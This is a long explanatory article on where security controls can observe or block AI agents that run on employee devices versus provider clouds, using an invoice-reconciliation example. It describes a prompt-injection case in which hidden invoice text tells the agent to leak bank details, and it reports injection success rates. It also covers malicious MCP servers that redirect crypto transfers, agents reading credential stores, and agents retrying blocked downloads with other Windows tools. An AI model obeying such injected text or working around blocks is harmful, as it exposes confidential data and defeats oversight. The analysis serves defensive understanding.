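# Where the security perimeter lies for cloud-hosted and endpoint-resident AI agents

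## What are the parts of an AI agent, and what is its security perimeter?

An AI agent is a program that uses a language model to carry out a task by taking actions, such as reading files, running commands or sending messages, with limited supervision. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) adopts a definition from the software developer Simon Willison, in which an agent runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal. Some agents run on an employee's computer, some run on their provider's servers, and others combine the two. The location matters for security because a company can inspect or stop an action only at a point that it controls or that the provider opens to it.

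Suppose an accounts employee asks an agent to reconcile a folder of invoices with the payments ledger and post a summary to the team's chat channel. This routine task gives the agent access to confidential files and lets it run code and post messages in the employee's name.

### The parts of an agent

The model receives a context, which here includes the employee's request and the contents of the invoices, and returns a text reply. One such run is called an inference. The model itself does not open files or post messages. A separate program, the agent loop (or harness), sends the context to the model, reads the reply and carries out any actions specified in it.

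Pirch and colleagues describe the steps of this cycle. When a request arrives, the loop puts it in a list of messages with the conversation so far, any stored preferences and descriptions of the available tools. The model's reply may contain a tool call, which is a structured request to run a particular tool with particular arguments. The loop parses the call, runs the tool, appends the result to the list and sends the longer list back to the model. The cycle ends when the model signals that the task is complete or the loop reaches a maximum number of steps.

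For the invoices, the first tool call might list the folder, and the next few might read each file. The model may then write a short script that matches invoice numbers against ledger entries. The loop sends the script to an execution sandbox, an isolated environment for running the agent's commands and code. To post the summary, the agent needs a connector, a link to an outside service that often follows a common standard, the Model Context Protocol (MCP). The chat service accepts the post because the connector presents a credential, typically a token that stands for the employee's permission.

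The work also leaves a stored history of the request, the invoice text, the script, its output and the summary. Pirch and colleagues point out that sensitive data may appear in the intermediate messages even when it is not in the final answer. For example, the team channel might receive only totals, while the history holds every supplier's bank details.

### Where each part can sit

These parts do not have to run on the same machine. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office tasks, divides them differently in local and cloud sessions. According to Anthropic's *Claude Cowork architecture overview*, the agent loop in a local session runs directly on the user's device, while shell commands and code run in a virtual machine, a simulated computer separate from the device's main operating system. In a cloud session, both the loop and the code run on Anthropic's servers. Those servers also make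 the connector calls, and the connector tokens stay outside the sandbox.

Where a session runs determines where its history is stored. Harmonic Security's *Securing Claude Cowork* (2026), a guide from a vendor that sells help with securing such agents, explains that cloud sessions are saved to the user's Claude account, while the history of local sessions stays on the user's machine, where administrators cannot delete it centrally. The model can also run elsewhere. Harmonic Security describes a mode in which the desktop program sends its inference to a service that the customer chooses, such as Amazon Bedrock.

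Four arrangements cover most of the possibilities.

| Arrangement | Model | Agent loop | Agent's code | Connectors and credentials | History | Example |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| All on the device except the model | Provider's servers | Device | Device | Largely on the device | Device | Claude Code in the desktop app |
| Code in a virtual machine on the device | Provider's servers | Device | Virtual machine on the device | Local connectors on the device | Device | Cowork local session |
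| Everything on the provider's servers | Provider's servers | Provider's servers | Sandbox on the provider's servers | Provider's servers, outside the sandbox | User's account with the provider | Cowork cloud session |
| Loop at the provider, code on customer machines | Provider's servers | Provider's servers | Customer's computers or servers | Depends on the product | Depends on the product | An agent that the provider hosts and that runs commands on a company's own server |

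Actual products don't always fit the table. For example, a Cowork cloud session can reach a folder on the employee's laptop through the Claude desktop app, but only while the app is open. If the invoices are on the laptop, the agent fetches copies of the ones it needs and processes them on Anthropic's servers. The loop and the code are then in the cloud, but one of the tools is on the laptop.

A provider can also move a task from one arrangement to another. According to Anthropic's *Use Claude Cowork on web, desktop, and mobile*, new Cowork tasks on the Pro, Max and Ultra plans have run in the cloud since October 6, 2026, and Anthropic removed the setting that had kept them on the user's computer. It directs people who still want local execution to Claude Code, its programming agent. Organisations with existing desktop deployments can continue to run local sessions. But on the affected plans,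 the same request about the same invoices now runs on different machines, even though the subscriber has changed nothing.

### What counts as a perimeter

An agent's security perimeter is the set of control points where a policy can observe, allow, change or block the agent's inputs and actions before they take effect. Examples include a prompt that asks the employee to approve a post and a firewall rule that refuses a connection. A log that an administrator reads the next morning is useful for an investigation, but it is not part of the perimeter in this sense because the summary has already reached the channel.

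Computer security has a classic test for whether a control point deserves trust. A component that rules on every attempt to use a protected resource is a reference monitor, and it has to meet three requirements:

- It checks every action, so that no route leads around it.
- The program under its control cannot tamper with it.
- It is small enough for people to verify that it works correctly.

Pirch and colleagues apply this kind of thinking to agents by comparing an agent to an operating system. The model corresponds to the user, whom the system treats as untrusted. Tools correspond to system calls, the requests an ordinary program makes when it needs the operating system to open a file or a connection. The agent's runtime, which is the software around the model, corresponds to the kernel, which grants or refuses those requests. The check on tool calls therefore belongs in the runtime or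 below it, not in the model.

Existing agents do not always meet that standard. Pirch and colleagues examined four agents in the style of OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs on the user's own machine and that third parties can extend. All four enforced their file access rules at the same privilege level as the code that processes incoming text. An attacker who takes over that code may therefore be able to reach the rules too, which the tampering requirement is meant to prevent. The study excluded coding agents on the ground that their makers control the environment more tightly, so its findings do not show how well commercial hosted agents perform.

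The invoice task shows how a control can meet part of the test and still leave a gap. Anthropic routes all traffic leaving a cloud session's sandbox through an egress proxy, a relay that permits only listed destinations, and states that the sandbox cannot reconfigure or bypass it. A list of destinations is also fairly easy to review, although customers have to rely on Anthropic's description of the proxy itself. The proxy would block the script from uploading the invoices to an unlisted website. However, the summary reaches the team channel through a connector call, which Anthropic's servers make outside the sandbox. If the model asked the connector to post the invoices in full, the post would not pass through the proxy. Harmonic Security likewise warns that the network setting does not cover web searches, web fetches or MCP connectors.

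### Why a network or a device makes a poor boundary

Companies have usually drawn their security perimeter around a place, traditionally the office network. They use a firewall to examine what enters and leaves, and they trust what is inside more. But an agent in the cloud can read a file from one online service and post to another without sending anything across that network.

The newer version of the perimeter surrounds the device, and companies already own several kinds of tools to secure it. Endpoint detection and response (EDR) is software on a device that records and blocks suspicious processes, file access and connections. Data loss prevention (DLP) tools detect sensitive data, such as the account numbers in an invoice, and stop it from leaving approved places. Mobile device management (MDM) lets an organisation configure all its devices centrally. With Claude's desktop app, for example,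 an administrator can use MDM to switch off connectors that run on the device.

Endpoint security tools can monitor the most when the agent's loop and code run as ordinary programs on the laptop. They can monitor less when the code runs in a virtual machine, and less still when it runs off the laptop. Anthropic tells customers that endpoint detection and response (EDR) tools cannot observe activity inside Cowork's virtual machine or in its cloud sessions.

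Security vendors disagree about what should replace the old boundary, and their answers tend to match their products. In IT Brew's *Does the agentic era signal the end of cybersecurity perimeters?*, Cristian Rodriguez of CrowdStrike, which sells endpoint security, places the new perimeter at the endpoint and the identity each user presents to the company's services. The endpoint part of that answer suits an agent on a laptop but not one that runs wholly on a provider's servers, because an employee can start the invoice task from a phone, switch the phone off, and the agent will keep working.

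Identity carries over better, because the chat service still has to accept somebody's credential. But a credential shows who gave permission, not who is acting. Gavin Reid of Human Security, which sells tools for distinguishing automated from human traffic, told IT Brew that many back-end systems treat an agent's connection like a user's. Such a system can't tell a post the employee wrote from one an agent wrote under an attacker's influence.

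### Prompt injection

The attacker in that last case can use prompt injection without breaking into anything. Prompt injection is text in material an agent reads that causes the agent to follow an attacker's instructions. For example, a supplier, or someone posing as one, could send an invoice with a line in white type on a white background that tells the agent to include every supplier's bank details in its summary. The employee would not see the line, but the loop would extract it with the rest of the document and add it to the list of messages.

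The agent is vulnerable because the employee's request and the supplier's text reach the model in the same form, and the model has to infer which of them has authority. Pirch and colleagues found that all four agents they tested mixed trusted and untrusted data in one context. Developers often add warnings to the agent's standing instructions, but these only guide the model, and later text in the context can override them.

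Developers measure the problem with an attack success rate, the share of attempts in which the planted text gets the agent to do what the attacker intended. The rate depends heavily on how developers count successes. A per-attempt rate treats every try separately, while a per-scenario rate counts the test environments in which at least one try succeeded. VentureBeat's *Anthropic’s browser agent got hijacked 31.5% of the time before safeguards engaged* describes the per-scenario rate as the harder measure. The rate also depends on the attacker. In an earlier account of its browser extension, Anthropic described testing with an adaptive attacker, a system that tries and combines many techniques known to work.

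Anthropic released Claude Opus 5 with its *System Card* (2026) on July 24. Harmonic Security reports Anthropic's figures for attacks from red-teamers, people who try to break a system to test it. The attack success rate against Opus 5 was 3.8% without added safeguards and 0% with them. The safeguards were probes that look for injections and a classifier that verifies the agent's actions. For browser agents, The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* gives an attack success rate of zero across 129 scenarios. The *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, which followed on September 22, reports similar or better results on every injection test, but also says the newer model is, at least in some circumstances, more likely than earlier ones to follow malicious instructions.

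Safeguards sharply reduced the success rate of attacks on an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.8, from May 2026. VentureBeat reports that when the model ran as a browser agent with extended reasoning on, attacks succeeded in 31.5% of attempts without safeguards and 0.5% with them.

Another test, from the security firm Gray Swan, allows attackers repeated attempts. *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026) reproduces the results. Attackers succeeded against Opus 5 in 0.2% of cases with one attempt and 2.0% within 15 attempts, compared with 0.5% and 5.5% for Opus 4.8. Within 15 attempts, they succeeded in 16.5% of cases against Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. The comparison is Anthropic's own and favours its product.

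These are large improvements, but a low attack success rate is not a security boundary. If 0.2% held outside the benchmark, an attacker who sent one poisoned invoice to each of 500 companies could expect about one success. Rates also vary with the setting. VentureBeat reported that Claude Opus 4.6, from February 2026, resisted all 200 attempts in a constrained coding environment without safeguards. When the same model operated a graphical interface without safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt, the attacker had succeeded in 78.6% of cases without safeguards and 57.1% with them.

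Published rates also cover only the attacks that the testers tried. Discussing a separate challenge in which some 6,000 attempts failed, Willison (2026) agreed that training makes injection much harder. He still advised against any system in which a successful injection could do irreversible damage, since a more sophisticated attacker might get through. He later highlighted a claim by Johann Rehberger, a researcher he considers one of the most credible in the field. Rehberger's attack on Claude Code with Opus 5 reportedly works 80% of the time against auto mode, the default setting Anthropic relies on to protect users from injection. According to The Decoder, OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that injection may never be fully solved.

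Better scores do not change the model's status, because it still fails the reference-monitor test. Anyone who can give the model text, such as an invoice, can try to tamper with its judgement. Nor can anyone verify a large language model as they could a short list of permitted destinations. The safeguard classifiers lower the risk considerably, but they also judge by learned patterns, and someone may find an input that they misjudge. A rule outside the model does not depend on that judgement. If the connector's credential permits posts only to the accounts channel, no wording in an invoice can send the summary to another channel. Keeping bank details out of the accounts channel itself would require a separate check on the post's content.

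## What can a company see and stop when agents run on its devices?

When the agent loop runs on an employee's computer, a company can enforce rules outside the model at four layers. EDR monitors the whole device. An operating-system sandbox limits what the agent's commands can reach. Client-side hooks are checks that the agent program runs before or after a step. Centrally managed settings control how employees can configure the program. The table uses Claude Code as an example for the last three because Anthropic documents them in detail.

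| Layer | What it shows | What it can block | Who can switch it off |
|---|---|---|---|
| EDR | Processes, file access and connections on the device | Activity that matches a detection rule | Usually only an administrator |
| Operating-system sandbox | The files and domains a command tries to reach | Access outside the permitted folders and domains | The user, unless an administrator enforces it |
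| Client-side hooks | The user's prompt, and each tool call with its arguments | A prompt or tool call before it takes effect | The user, except for hooks that an administrator installs |
| Centrally managed settings | Nothing by themselves | Features and modes of the agent they configure | An administrator |

### Endpoint detection and response

If the invoice task ran in Claude Code on a laptop, EDR would record the agent starting Python, the script reading the invoice folder and any connection the script opened. EDR compares this activity with rules that describe how attackers behave, and it can block a match immediately. It normally runs with higher privileges than the employee's programs, so an employee without administrator rights cannot turn it off, and nor can an agent running with that employee's rights. Developers often have administrator rights, which weakens the protection on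 their machines.

EDR vendors wrote many of these rules when only an intruder was likely to trigger them. *When AI agents look like attackers* (2026), by the endpoint security vendor Sophos, examines how coding agents have changed that. Sophos analysed seven days of data from June 2026 from Windows machines that run its software. It looked at the rules that agents such as Claude Code, Cursor and OpenAI's Codex had triggered, directly or through programs they started, and counted machines rather than individual alerts.

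Of the hits on rules that block an action, 56.2% involved access to credentials and 28.8% involved running suspicious code. Another 4.1% came from a feature that stopped agents from running programs with a low reputation score, though none of those programs appeared malicious. Hits on rules that silently record activity fell mostly under evasion of defences (38.5%) and command and control (34.0%), the category for traffic an attacker uses to direct a compromised machine.

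One rule produced 42.6% of the blocking hits for credentials. It fires when a program uses a Windows function to decrypt passwords or other secrets stored by a browser. In Sophos's example, Claude Code was automating a browser with GStack, a popular pack of add-on skills, and the skill decrypted browser data along the way. Sophos considers this almost certainly harmless but thinks the rule was right to fire. In another case, Claude closed several browser processes, ran a Python script that opened the browser's credential stores, and listed the credentials saved in Windows. Someone had started that session with an option that skips Claude Code's permission prompts. The Hacker News (2026) notes that defenders have long treated such behaviour as a strong sign of an attack.

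Agents also resemble intruders in how they respond to a block. Codex tried to download a Python installer from Python's official website using certutil, a Windows certificate tool that attackers often misuse to fetch files. Sophos's software blocked it. Over the next ten minutes the agent tried several variations, then switched to bitsadmin, another built-in Windows tool, but the software blocked every attempt. Changing methods after a block used to be a good sign of a live attacker rather than a simple script, but harmless agents now do it routinely.

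Security teams can therefore expect more false alarms, but the data doesn't show how many because Sophos published percentages without the number of machines. Sophos says the shift is not yet large. It has already adjusted a rule, written more than five years ago to catch disguised PowerShell commands, because agents now format commands in a similar way. It would keep other rules, since decrypting stored passwords is risky whether a person or an agent starts it. A company could silence the alarms by exempting everything an agent starts, but that would also exempt an agent following instructions hidden in an invoice.

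### Operating-system sandboxes

A sandbox limits what a command can reach, and the operating system enforces those limits regardless of the command's purpose. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code applies the limits to shell commands and every process they start. By default, sandboxed commands can write to the working folder and a temporary folder, and need approval the first time they contact a new domain.

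The default limits on reading are looser. An earlier version of Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, from June 2026, warns that sandboxed commands can read almost the whole computer, including files that hold developers' cloud credentials and server login keys. An administrator or user has to list those folders to block them. The network check compares the destination's name with a list but does not decrypt the traffic, so it cannot inspect what a command sends to a permitted domain.

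Claude Code's sandbox is off by default. It does not work on native Windows, or on other systems if a required component is missing, and in those cases Claude Code runs commands without it. When a command fails inside the sandbox, the agent may try to rerun it outside. Depending on the permission mode, the user or a classifier decides whether to allow this, or the command runs automatically. Anthropic notes that a user's standing rule approving a type of command also approves the retry.

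Some of the agent's actions bypass the sandbox even when it is on. Claude Code's built-in tools for reading and editing files follow separate permission rules, so if a company blocked the payroll folder only in the sandbox's read settings, the invoice task's script could not open it, but the agent's file-reading tool might. Local MCP servers, the programs that provide many of an agent's connectors, also run outside the sandbox, with the user's full access.

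*AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) proposes an access control system for those servers. Each server comes with a manifest, a short file that lists the general capabilities it needs, such as reading files or contacting the network. The format borrows from Android's permission system. AgentBound runs the server in a container, an isolated environment that starts with no access. The user turns each general capability into a specific permission, such as access to one folder or one web address. AgentBound stops any request that the manifest does not cover. Developers do not have to change the server's code.

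Writing manifests by hand for thousands of servers would be slow, so the researchers used language models to draft them from source code. They drafted manifests for 296 popular servers and asked the developers of 96 of them to check the results. The reported accuracy of 80.9% corresponds to only 17 acceptances and 4 rejections, because about three-quarters of the developers did not respond. In a separate check of 48 servers, the drafts agreed with manifests written by two of the researchers on 96.5% of the capability decisions. Most of the errors left out a capability the server needed, which would break a function rather than create a security hole.

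In a test on 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections, AgentBound stopped eight outright and part of a ninth. One of the eight was a maps server that secretly replaced Google's address with an attacker's. The attack failed because the container allowed connections only to Google. The attacks that succeeded stayed within the permissions or did not touch system resources. For example, a server that reports the time carried a hidden instruction for the model to redirect cryptocurrency transfers made through a different server. Both servers stayed within their permissions, so AgentBound did not block the attack.

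Running servers in containers added little delay. Startup generally took about 100 to 400 milliseconds longer. After that, common operations such as reading a file took on average 0.6 milliseconds longer on a Mac and 0.29 milliseconds longer on Linux. An agent usually starts a server once and calls it many times, and a single run of the model takes far longer than any of these delays.

### Client-side hooks

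A client-side hook works inside the agent loop, so it receives information that EDR normally lacks. Before Claude Code runs a tool call, it can send the tool's name and arguments to a script or web address the company chooses. In Anthropic's example, a script checks for a command that deletes whole folders. If the script finds one, it returns a denial, and Claude Code blocks the call and tells the model why.

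Besides refusing a call, a hook can approve it, ask the user to decide, or rewrite it, for instance to put a file in a different folder. If several hooks disagree, a denial overrides the rest. A hook can also check the employee's prompt before the model processes it. After a tool has run, a hook can replace the output before it reaches the model, according to Anthropic's guide for developers who build their own agents. In the invoice task, such a hook could mask the account numbers in each invoice, so the model would have no bank details to post.

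A hook covers only the tools its author thought of. The same guide includes a hook that protects a file of secrets by checking Claude's tools for writing and editing files. If the model changes the file with a shell command instead, the hook does not run. On Windows, the hook also fails to block the writing tool, because it looks for a forward slash in the file's path and Windows uses a backslash. Anthropic advises developers to use the sandbox settings to stop shell commands from changing the file.

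Hooks also fail open by default on most events. If a script crashes, takes too long or has a mistyped path, Claude Code usually continues to its normal permission checks. Even the standard error code for a failed program does not block the action. Anthropic offers a setting that blocks the action when a hook fails, but someone has to add it to each hook. A company that tests only whether its hook catches a forbidden command may never notice that the hook does nothing when the script is missing.

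Users can disable their own hooks with one setting, but they cannot disable hooks an administrator installs through managed settings. The agent may also be able to change unprotected settings, because it runs with the user's permissions. Anthropic warns that if a user turns off the sandbox's file restrictions and lets commands run without approval, a command can edit Claude Code's settings and give itself wider access the next time it runs. Managed hooks avoid that problem, but they run only when Claude Code calls them, so they don't apply if a person switches to another agent.

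### Centrally managed settings

Managed settings determine whether the other controls are on and who can change them, but they do not monitor anything. A company can distribute them as a file through MDM or from Anthropic's servers. Anthropic's sample policy sets Claude Code to turn on the sandbox, not to start if the sandbox is unavailable, and to ignore requests to run a failed command outside it. Together, these settings close the main gaps in the sandbox's default behaviour. A company with Windows laptops can't simply apply the policy everywhere, because the sandbox is unavailable on native Windows and Claude Code would not start there.

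When a Claude Code setting is either on or off, the administrator's value overrides the developer's. When a setting is a list, Claude Code combines their entries, so a developer can add exceptions. Administrators can restrict the lists of permitted domains and readable folders to their own entries, but in June 2026 they could not do this for the list of commands that run outside the sandbox. Anthropic has since narrowed this gap. It says that when an administrator disables unsandboxed retries, Claude Code now ignores exceptions in a project's own files, which prevents a downloaded project from loosening the rules.

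For Cowork, administrators can use MDM to block desktop extensions (packages that add tools) and connectors that run on the device. According to Anthropic, both settings apply to the device, not the organisation's account, so they have no effect on computers the company does not manage. They also do not control other vendors' agents on the same machine. To find or block those, a company needs something that monitors the whole device.

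### Intent and action

EDR and the agent's own log each record only part of a task. In the invoice task, EDR would show that the agent started Python and that Python read a folder and opened a connection. It would not show whether the employee had asked for this or a hidden line in an invoice had caused it. The agent's log would contain the employee's request and the tool call that ran the script, but it might not show the other programs the script started.

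Sophos ran into this problem in its own data. Cursor ran a script that tried to place a file in the Windows startup folder, where it would run at every login, and a rule blocked the attempt. Intruders use the same method to keep their access to a machine. The file's name suggested a link to an application called EZConvert, but the analysts could not confirm what the agent had been trying to do because they did not have the script's contents.

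Sysdig, which sells monitoring for running software, has published an early estimate of the gap. Help Net Security's *Sysdig AI Defense puts runtime guardrails on AI agents* reports that the operating system's kernel records about seven processes for every action in an agent's log. The announcement does not describe the method, the agents or the tasks. A single command to install a package or build a program commonly starts several others, so a log that lists only the command is incomplete but not false, and the ratio does not mean that agents conceal most of what they do.

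The ratio does show why a company might want both records. Sysdig's chief technology officer, Loris Degioanni, argues that an agent's account of its work is useful context but not evidence, because the agent can misreport a tool call. He would treat any case where the account differs from what ran as a warning sign. Sysdig's product therefore collects tool calls and their arguments from the agent loop, and process activity from the kernel. Sysdig claims that a compromised agent cannot tamper with the kernel record.

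### How EDR vendors connect prompts to processes

EDR can already trace a process back to an agent through the chain of programs that started it, which is how Sophos identified the activity in its study. Newer products try to add the prompt and the tool call to the start of that chain. Falcon Guardian, announced on September 1, 2026, links the user's prompt and identity to each tool call and every resulting action on the system, according to CrowdStrike (2026). An analyst investigating the startup file could, in principle, trace the blocked action back to the request that led to it.

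Guardian also lists the agents on Windows and macOS computers, including those employees installed without permission, and blocks any the company has not approved. CrowdStrike describes some other parts as future features, including a gateway that would apply policy to MCP connections and to traffic between the company and AI services.

Microsoft took a similar approach in Defender, its security software. In June, it announced a preview that could find more than 20 types of local agent on Windows and macOS (Shteinberg, 2026, *The next frontier in endpoint security*). For each agent, Defender records the user, the device and risk factors such as a setting that approves actions automatically. It also maps the cloud services the user's account can reach. In Microsoft's example, a ChatGPT desktop agent has no cloud permissions of its own but inherits access to storage and encryption keys from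 an Amazon Web Services account.

At the time of the announcement, Defender could block Claude Code and GitHub Copilot's command-line agent, far fewer agents than it could find. Blocking for OpenClaw and Codex was due later. One of Shteinberg's illustrations shows Defender stopping malicious instructions in a tool call's result, so it can act on some of the text an agent reads as well as on the processes the agent starts.

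CrowdStrike advertises "hyper-accurate detections" across its platform, and Microsoft says Defender blocks in real time. Neither announcement gives a detection rate, a false alarm rate or a measured delay, and neither cites an independent test. The false alarm rate matters most for a tool that blocks developers' work automatically. A company can estimate it before turning on blocking by running the product in alert mode on ordinary agent tasks, including the browser automation and software downloads that triggered Sophos's rules.

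### Isolation also hides the agent

A virtual machine can protect a computer better than a sandbox that shares the computer's kernel. *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) describes an experimental tool that runs all of Claude Code on a Mac inside a microVM, a small virtual machine with its own stripped-down Linux kernel. A hostile agent would have to break out of the virtual machine to attack the Mac itself. Claude's login credentials normally stay outside the virtual machine, where a relay adds them to the agent's requests. The user can also cut off all network access except the connection to Anthropic's model.

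SideKernel shares the current folder with the agent, which can read, change or delete anything in it. Prasakis accepted this risk for convenience, because many developers do not use a sandbox at all. In his informal survey of 68 coding-agent users, 38.2% currently ran their agents in a sandbox and 51.5% never had. A third of the respondents worked in security, so he expects the real share of sandbox users to be lower.

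In a feature comparison, SideKernel passed 19 of 23 tests, the same number as Docker Sandboxes. Three other tools passed 12 each. The tests covered practical features such as sharing files and keeping settings after a restart, but did not measure resistance to attack. Prasakis both built SideKernel and ran the tests. He did not measure its overhead, and nobody has formally reviewed its security.

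This protection also makes the agent harder to monitor. SideKernel does not log the files the agent opens, the processes it starts or the outside addresses it contacts. EDR on the Mac would record the virtual machine as a program and could record changes to the shared folder, but it would not show the individual commands run inside it. A sandbox can make up for this by keeping its own records. Docker Sandboxes, for example, lists the domains the agent has contacted. But a security team would have to collect and check those records separately from its EDR data.

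Companies face the same problem with Cowork, a commercial product. In a local session, EDR can monitor the agent loop like any other program as it reads and writes files, fetches web pages and starts local MCP servers. It cannot monitor the shell commands and code that run inside the virtual machine, which has its own restrictions on network access. If the virtual machine cannot start, the commands and code do not run, but the file and web tools still work. For the invoice task, EDR could record the app opening the invoices but not what the script did with them.

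Anthropic states that Cowork's virtual machine is isolated by design from security tools on the device, and it tells companies that rely on endpoint monitoring for compliance to account for this before they introduce Cowork. EDR on a laptop running Cowork cannot inspect the code that the agent executes, although CrowdStrike calls the endpoint the only enforcement point with complete visibility of what agents execute. Team and Enterprise administrators can export records of Cowork's activity through OpenTelemetry, a common standard for monitoring data. These records help an investigation, but they do not let the company's EDR stop a command inside the virtual machine or in a Cowork cloud session.

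## What changes when the agent runs on a provider's cloud?

When an agent runs on a provider's servers, an employer can no longer inspect the agent's work through the employee's device. The provider decides which checks exist and which ones customers can adjust. Claude Cowork is a good case study because Anthropic moved it from the device to the cloud within a year.

### How Cowork moved

Cowork launched on January 12 as a research preview for Max subscribers on macOS, according to Anthropic's *Release notes* (2026). It ran on the user's computer and used a virtual machine for code. On July 7, in beta, Anthropic extended Cowork to the web and mobile and began running sessions on its own servers. As the rollout widened, Android Authority reported that sessions now ran in the cloud by default.

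Anthropic's stated reasons for moving the virtual machine from users' computers to the cloud were mostly practical. *A quote from Felix Rieseberg* (Willison, 2026) reproduces an explanation from Rieseberg, an Anthropic employee. Rieseberg says Anthropic had added the local virtual machine for capability, safety and security, but users disliked how much disk space, battery and processing power it took, and that closing the laptop stopped the work.

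The move affects ordinary office data more than program code. Anthropic's *Claude Cowork is coming to mobile and web* reports that more than 90% of Cowork use was not software development. One of its examples, reconciling a quarter's spending, is similar to the invoice task.

Whether an employee's work runs in the cloud depends on the plan, and the defaults are still changing. The table is current as of late November 2026. Its last column covers a newer version of Claude that merges chat and Cowork. According to Anthropic's *Claude Cowork and chat come together for Enterprise* (2026), every conversation in that version begins as a chat and continues in the cloud when a task has to run code or work with files.

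| Plan | Cowork sessions in the cloud | Merged chat and Cowork |
|---|---|---|
| Pro, Max and Ultra | All new tasks, with no setting to change this | Rolling out since September |
| Team | On by default, but an owner can turn them off | Due to turn on by default on December 1, unless an owner declines |
| Enterprise | Off until an owner turns them on and grants access to a group | Available since October 23, and due to turn on by default on November 16 |

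The Enterprise date comes from PYMNTS's *Anthropic Merges Claude Chat and Cowork for Enterprise Users* (2026) and applies to existing organisations.

According to Anthropic's guide for Team plans, *Set up and manage the new unified Claude experience*, the merged version requires only a general setting that allows code execution and file creation in the cloud. It works even when both Cowork and Cowork in the cloud are off. A Team owner who turned off cloud Cowork for security reasons could therefore find that chats start moving into cloud sessions in December.

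The merged version also has no option to run tasks locally, according to Anthropic's *What to expect with Claude Cowork in the cloud*. Anthropic intends to retire the separate version for Team plans on February 1, 2027, so most Team customers will lose local Cowork sessions then. That date does not apply to organisations with a zero data retention agreement, under which Anthropic does not store their prompts and replies.

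Some healthcare customers cannot run Cowork in the cloud for now. Anthropic's contract for data covered by HIPAA, the US health privacy law, applies to Cowork only in a special local configuration. Anthropic disables cloud sessions in that configuration, and no setting turns them on.

### A cloud session step by step

Suppose the accounts employee starts the invoice task in a Cowork cloud session. Anthropic creates a sandbox for that session alone and destroys it when the session ends. Anthropic says that sandboxes do not share state and that it keeps them separate from its corporate, research and model-training systems.

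The agent loop shares this sandbox with the code, so a malicious script may be closer to the loop than it would be in a local session. This makes the controls outside the sandbox more important.

The merged version keeps its environment longer. Each chat that needs a virtual machine gets its own, which stops after a few idle minutes. Anthropic saves the disk as an encrypted snapshot, and the environment expires 30 days after it is created. If an instruction hidden in an invoice caused the agent to save a harmful script, it could still be on the disk when the employee returned to the chat.

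Once the agent has the invoices, its script compares them with the ledger. The sandbox cannot reach private or internal addresses, so the script cannot explore the company's network. It also cannot reach cloud metadata addresses, which cloud servers use to look up information about themselves, sometimes including credentials. These limits also block legitimate access, so if the ledger is on an internal server, the employee has to supply it as a file or through a connector.

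The company can allow the sandbox to reach no public addresses, only sites that distribute software packages, sites on a list the company writes, or all domains. No access is the default for Enterprise organisations. The egress proxy enforces the choice from outside the sandbox, but if an administrator permits all domains, a malicious script can upload the invoices to almost any public website.

Anthropic applies the network settings when a session starts, and later changes do not affect sessions already running. An administrator who removes a domain from the list after discovering an attack would still have to stop the current session separately.

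The sandbox holds only tokens that belong to the session and expire within hours, so a stolen token is of limited use. The chat service's token stays outside the sandbox, so a malicious script cannot copy it, but the model can still send a request to Anthropic's servers to post something with it.

At that point, Cowork can ask the employee for approval. By default, members must give approval in each task for connector tools that can make changes, such as posting a message. Owners decide whether members can save a permanent approval. Cowork exempts read-only tools if the connector labels them as such. Most custom connectors lack these labels, so Cowork asks for approval even when their tools only read data, which is inconvenient but cautious.

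Members of an organisation can choose a mode that approves the agent's actions automatically, unless an owner removes it. Most new tasks on Enterprise plans still start in manual mode, but Anthropic is making automatic approval the default on Team plans. When Anthropic announced cloud sessions in July, it promised that nothing would go out until the user had reviewed and approved it, but how far that still holds depends partly on the organisation's settings.

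When the task ends, the finished files are saved with the history in the employee's Claude account, but working files that the agent did not hand over are lost with the sandbox. Anthropic says Claude's memory, which stores facts from earlier conversations, can also carry information from a cloud task into later chats. A misleading statement in an invoice could affect later work if the agent stored it. Local sessions do not use memory.

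### The same task in both places

The next table compares the invoice task in a local session and a cloud session. It assumes the invoices are in a folder on the laptop, which a cloud session reaches through the Claude desktop app. The record is the main copy of what happened at each step.

| Step | Who can observe it | Who can block it | Where the record is |
|---|---|---|---|
| The employee submits the request | Both: Anthropic | Local: an owner, by disabling Cowork. Cloud: also by disabling cloud sessions or requiring a trusted device | Local: laptop. Cloud: Claude account |
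| The agent reads the invoices | Local: EDR and Anthropic. Cloud: EDR when the app reads the files, then only Anthropic | Both: EDR, and the app's limits on which folders it can open | Local: laptop. Cloud: Claude account |
| The model chooses the next action | Both: Anthropic | Both: Anthropic's safeguards | Local: laptop. Cloud: Claude account |
| The agent runs the script | Local: EDR, but only with a sensor in the virtual machine. Cloud: Anthropic | Local: the virtual machine's restrictions. Cloud: the sandbox's restrictions | Local: laptop. Cloud: Claude account |
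| The script contacts a website | Local: the virtual machine's filter, and the office firewall if the laptop is behind it. Cloud: Anthropic's proxy | The same controls, with the company choosing the permitted destinations | Local: laptop and any firewall log. Cloud: Claude account |
| The agent posts the summary | Both: Anthropic and the chat service | Both: the employee, an owner through connector rules, and the chat service | Both: the chat service and the session history |

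Anthropic now lets administrators run their EDR sensor (fourth row) inside Cowork's local virtual machine, in beta on macOS and Windows. This narrows the gap in local monitoring but does not cover cloud sessions.

The two sessions differ most while the script runs and contacts other computers, because in the cloud those steps leave no trace on the laptop or the office network. The sessions differ least when the agent posts the summary, the step that would leak the bank details in the attack described earlier. In both cases, the chat service receives a valid request with a valid credential.

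Companies can still get records of cloud sessions. Help Net Security's *Security tools can now scan Claude Enterprise chats and uploads* (2026) describes Anthropic's Compliance API, which sends prompts, replies and tool calls from Cowork to a company's monitoring tools. On Enterprise plans, only the Primary Owner, the account's most senior administrator, can switch it on, so a security team may need that person's help to get the records.

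Enterprise administrators can retrieve local sessions through the same API. The cloud can still simplify record-keeping, because the history is in one place rather than scattered across laptops. Running the agent there also puts a copy of the invoices' contents on the provider's servers.

### How other hosted agents separate sessions

Other hosted agents also isolate each piece of work, but they differ in how they handle networks and credentials. Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments* explains that customers using Claude Code's cloud sessions can set the level of network access and run a setup script before the work begins. They can also store network secrets that, like Cowork's connector tokens, the agent can use but its code cannot read or copy.

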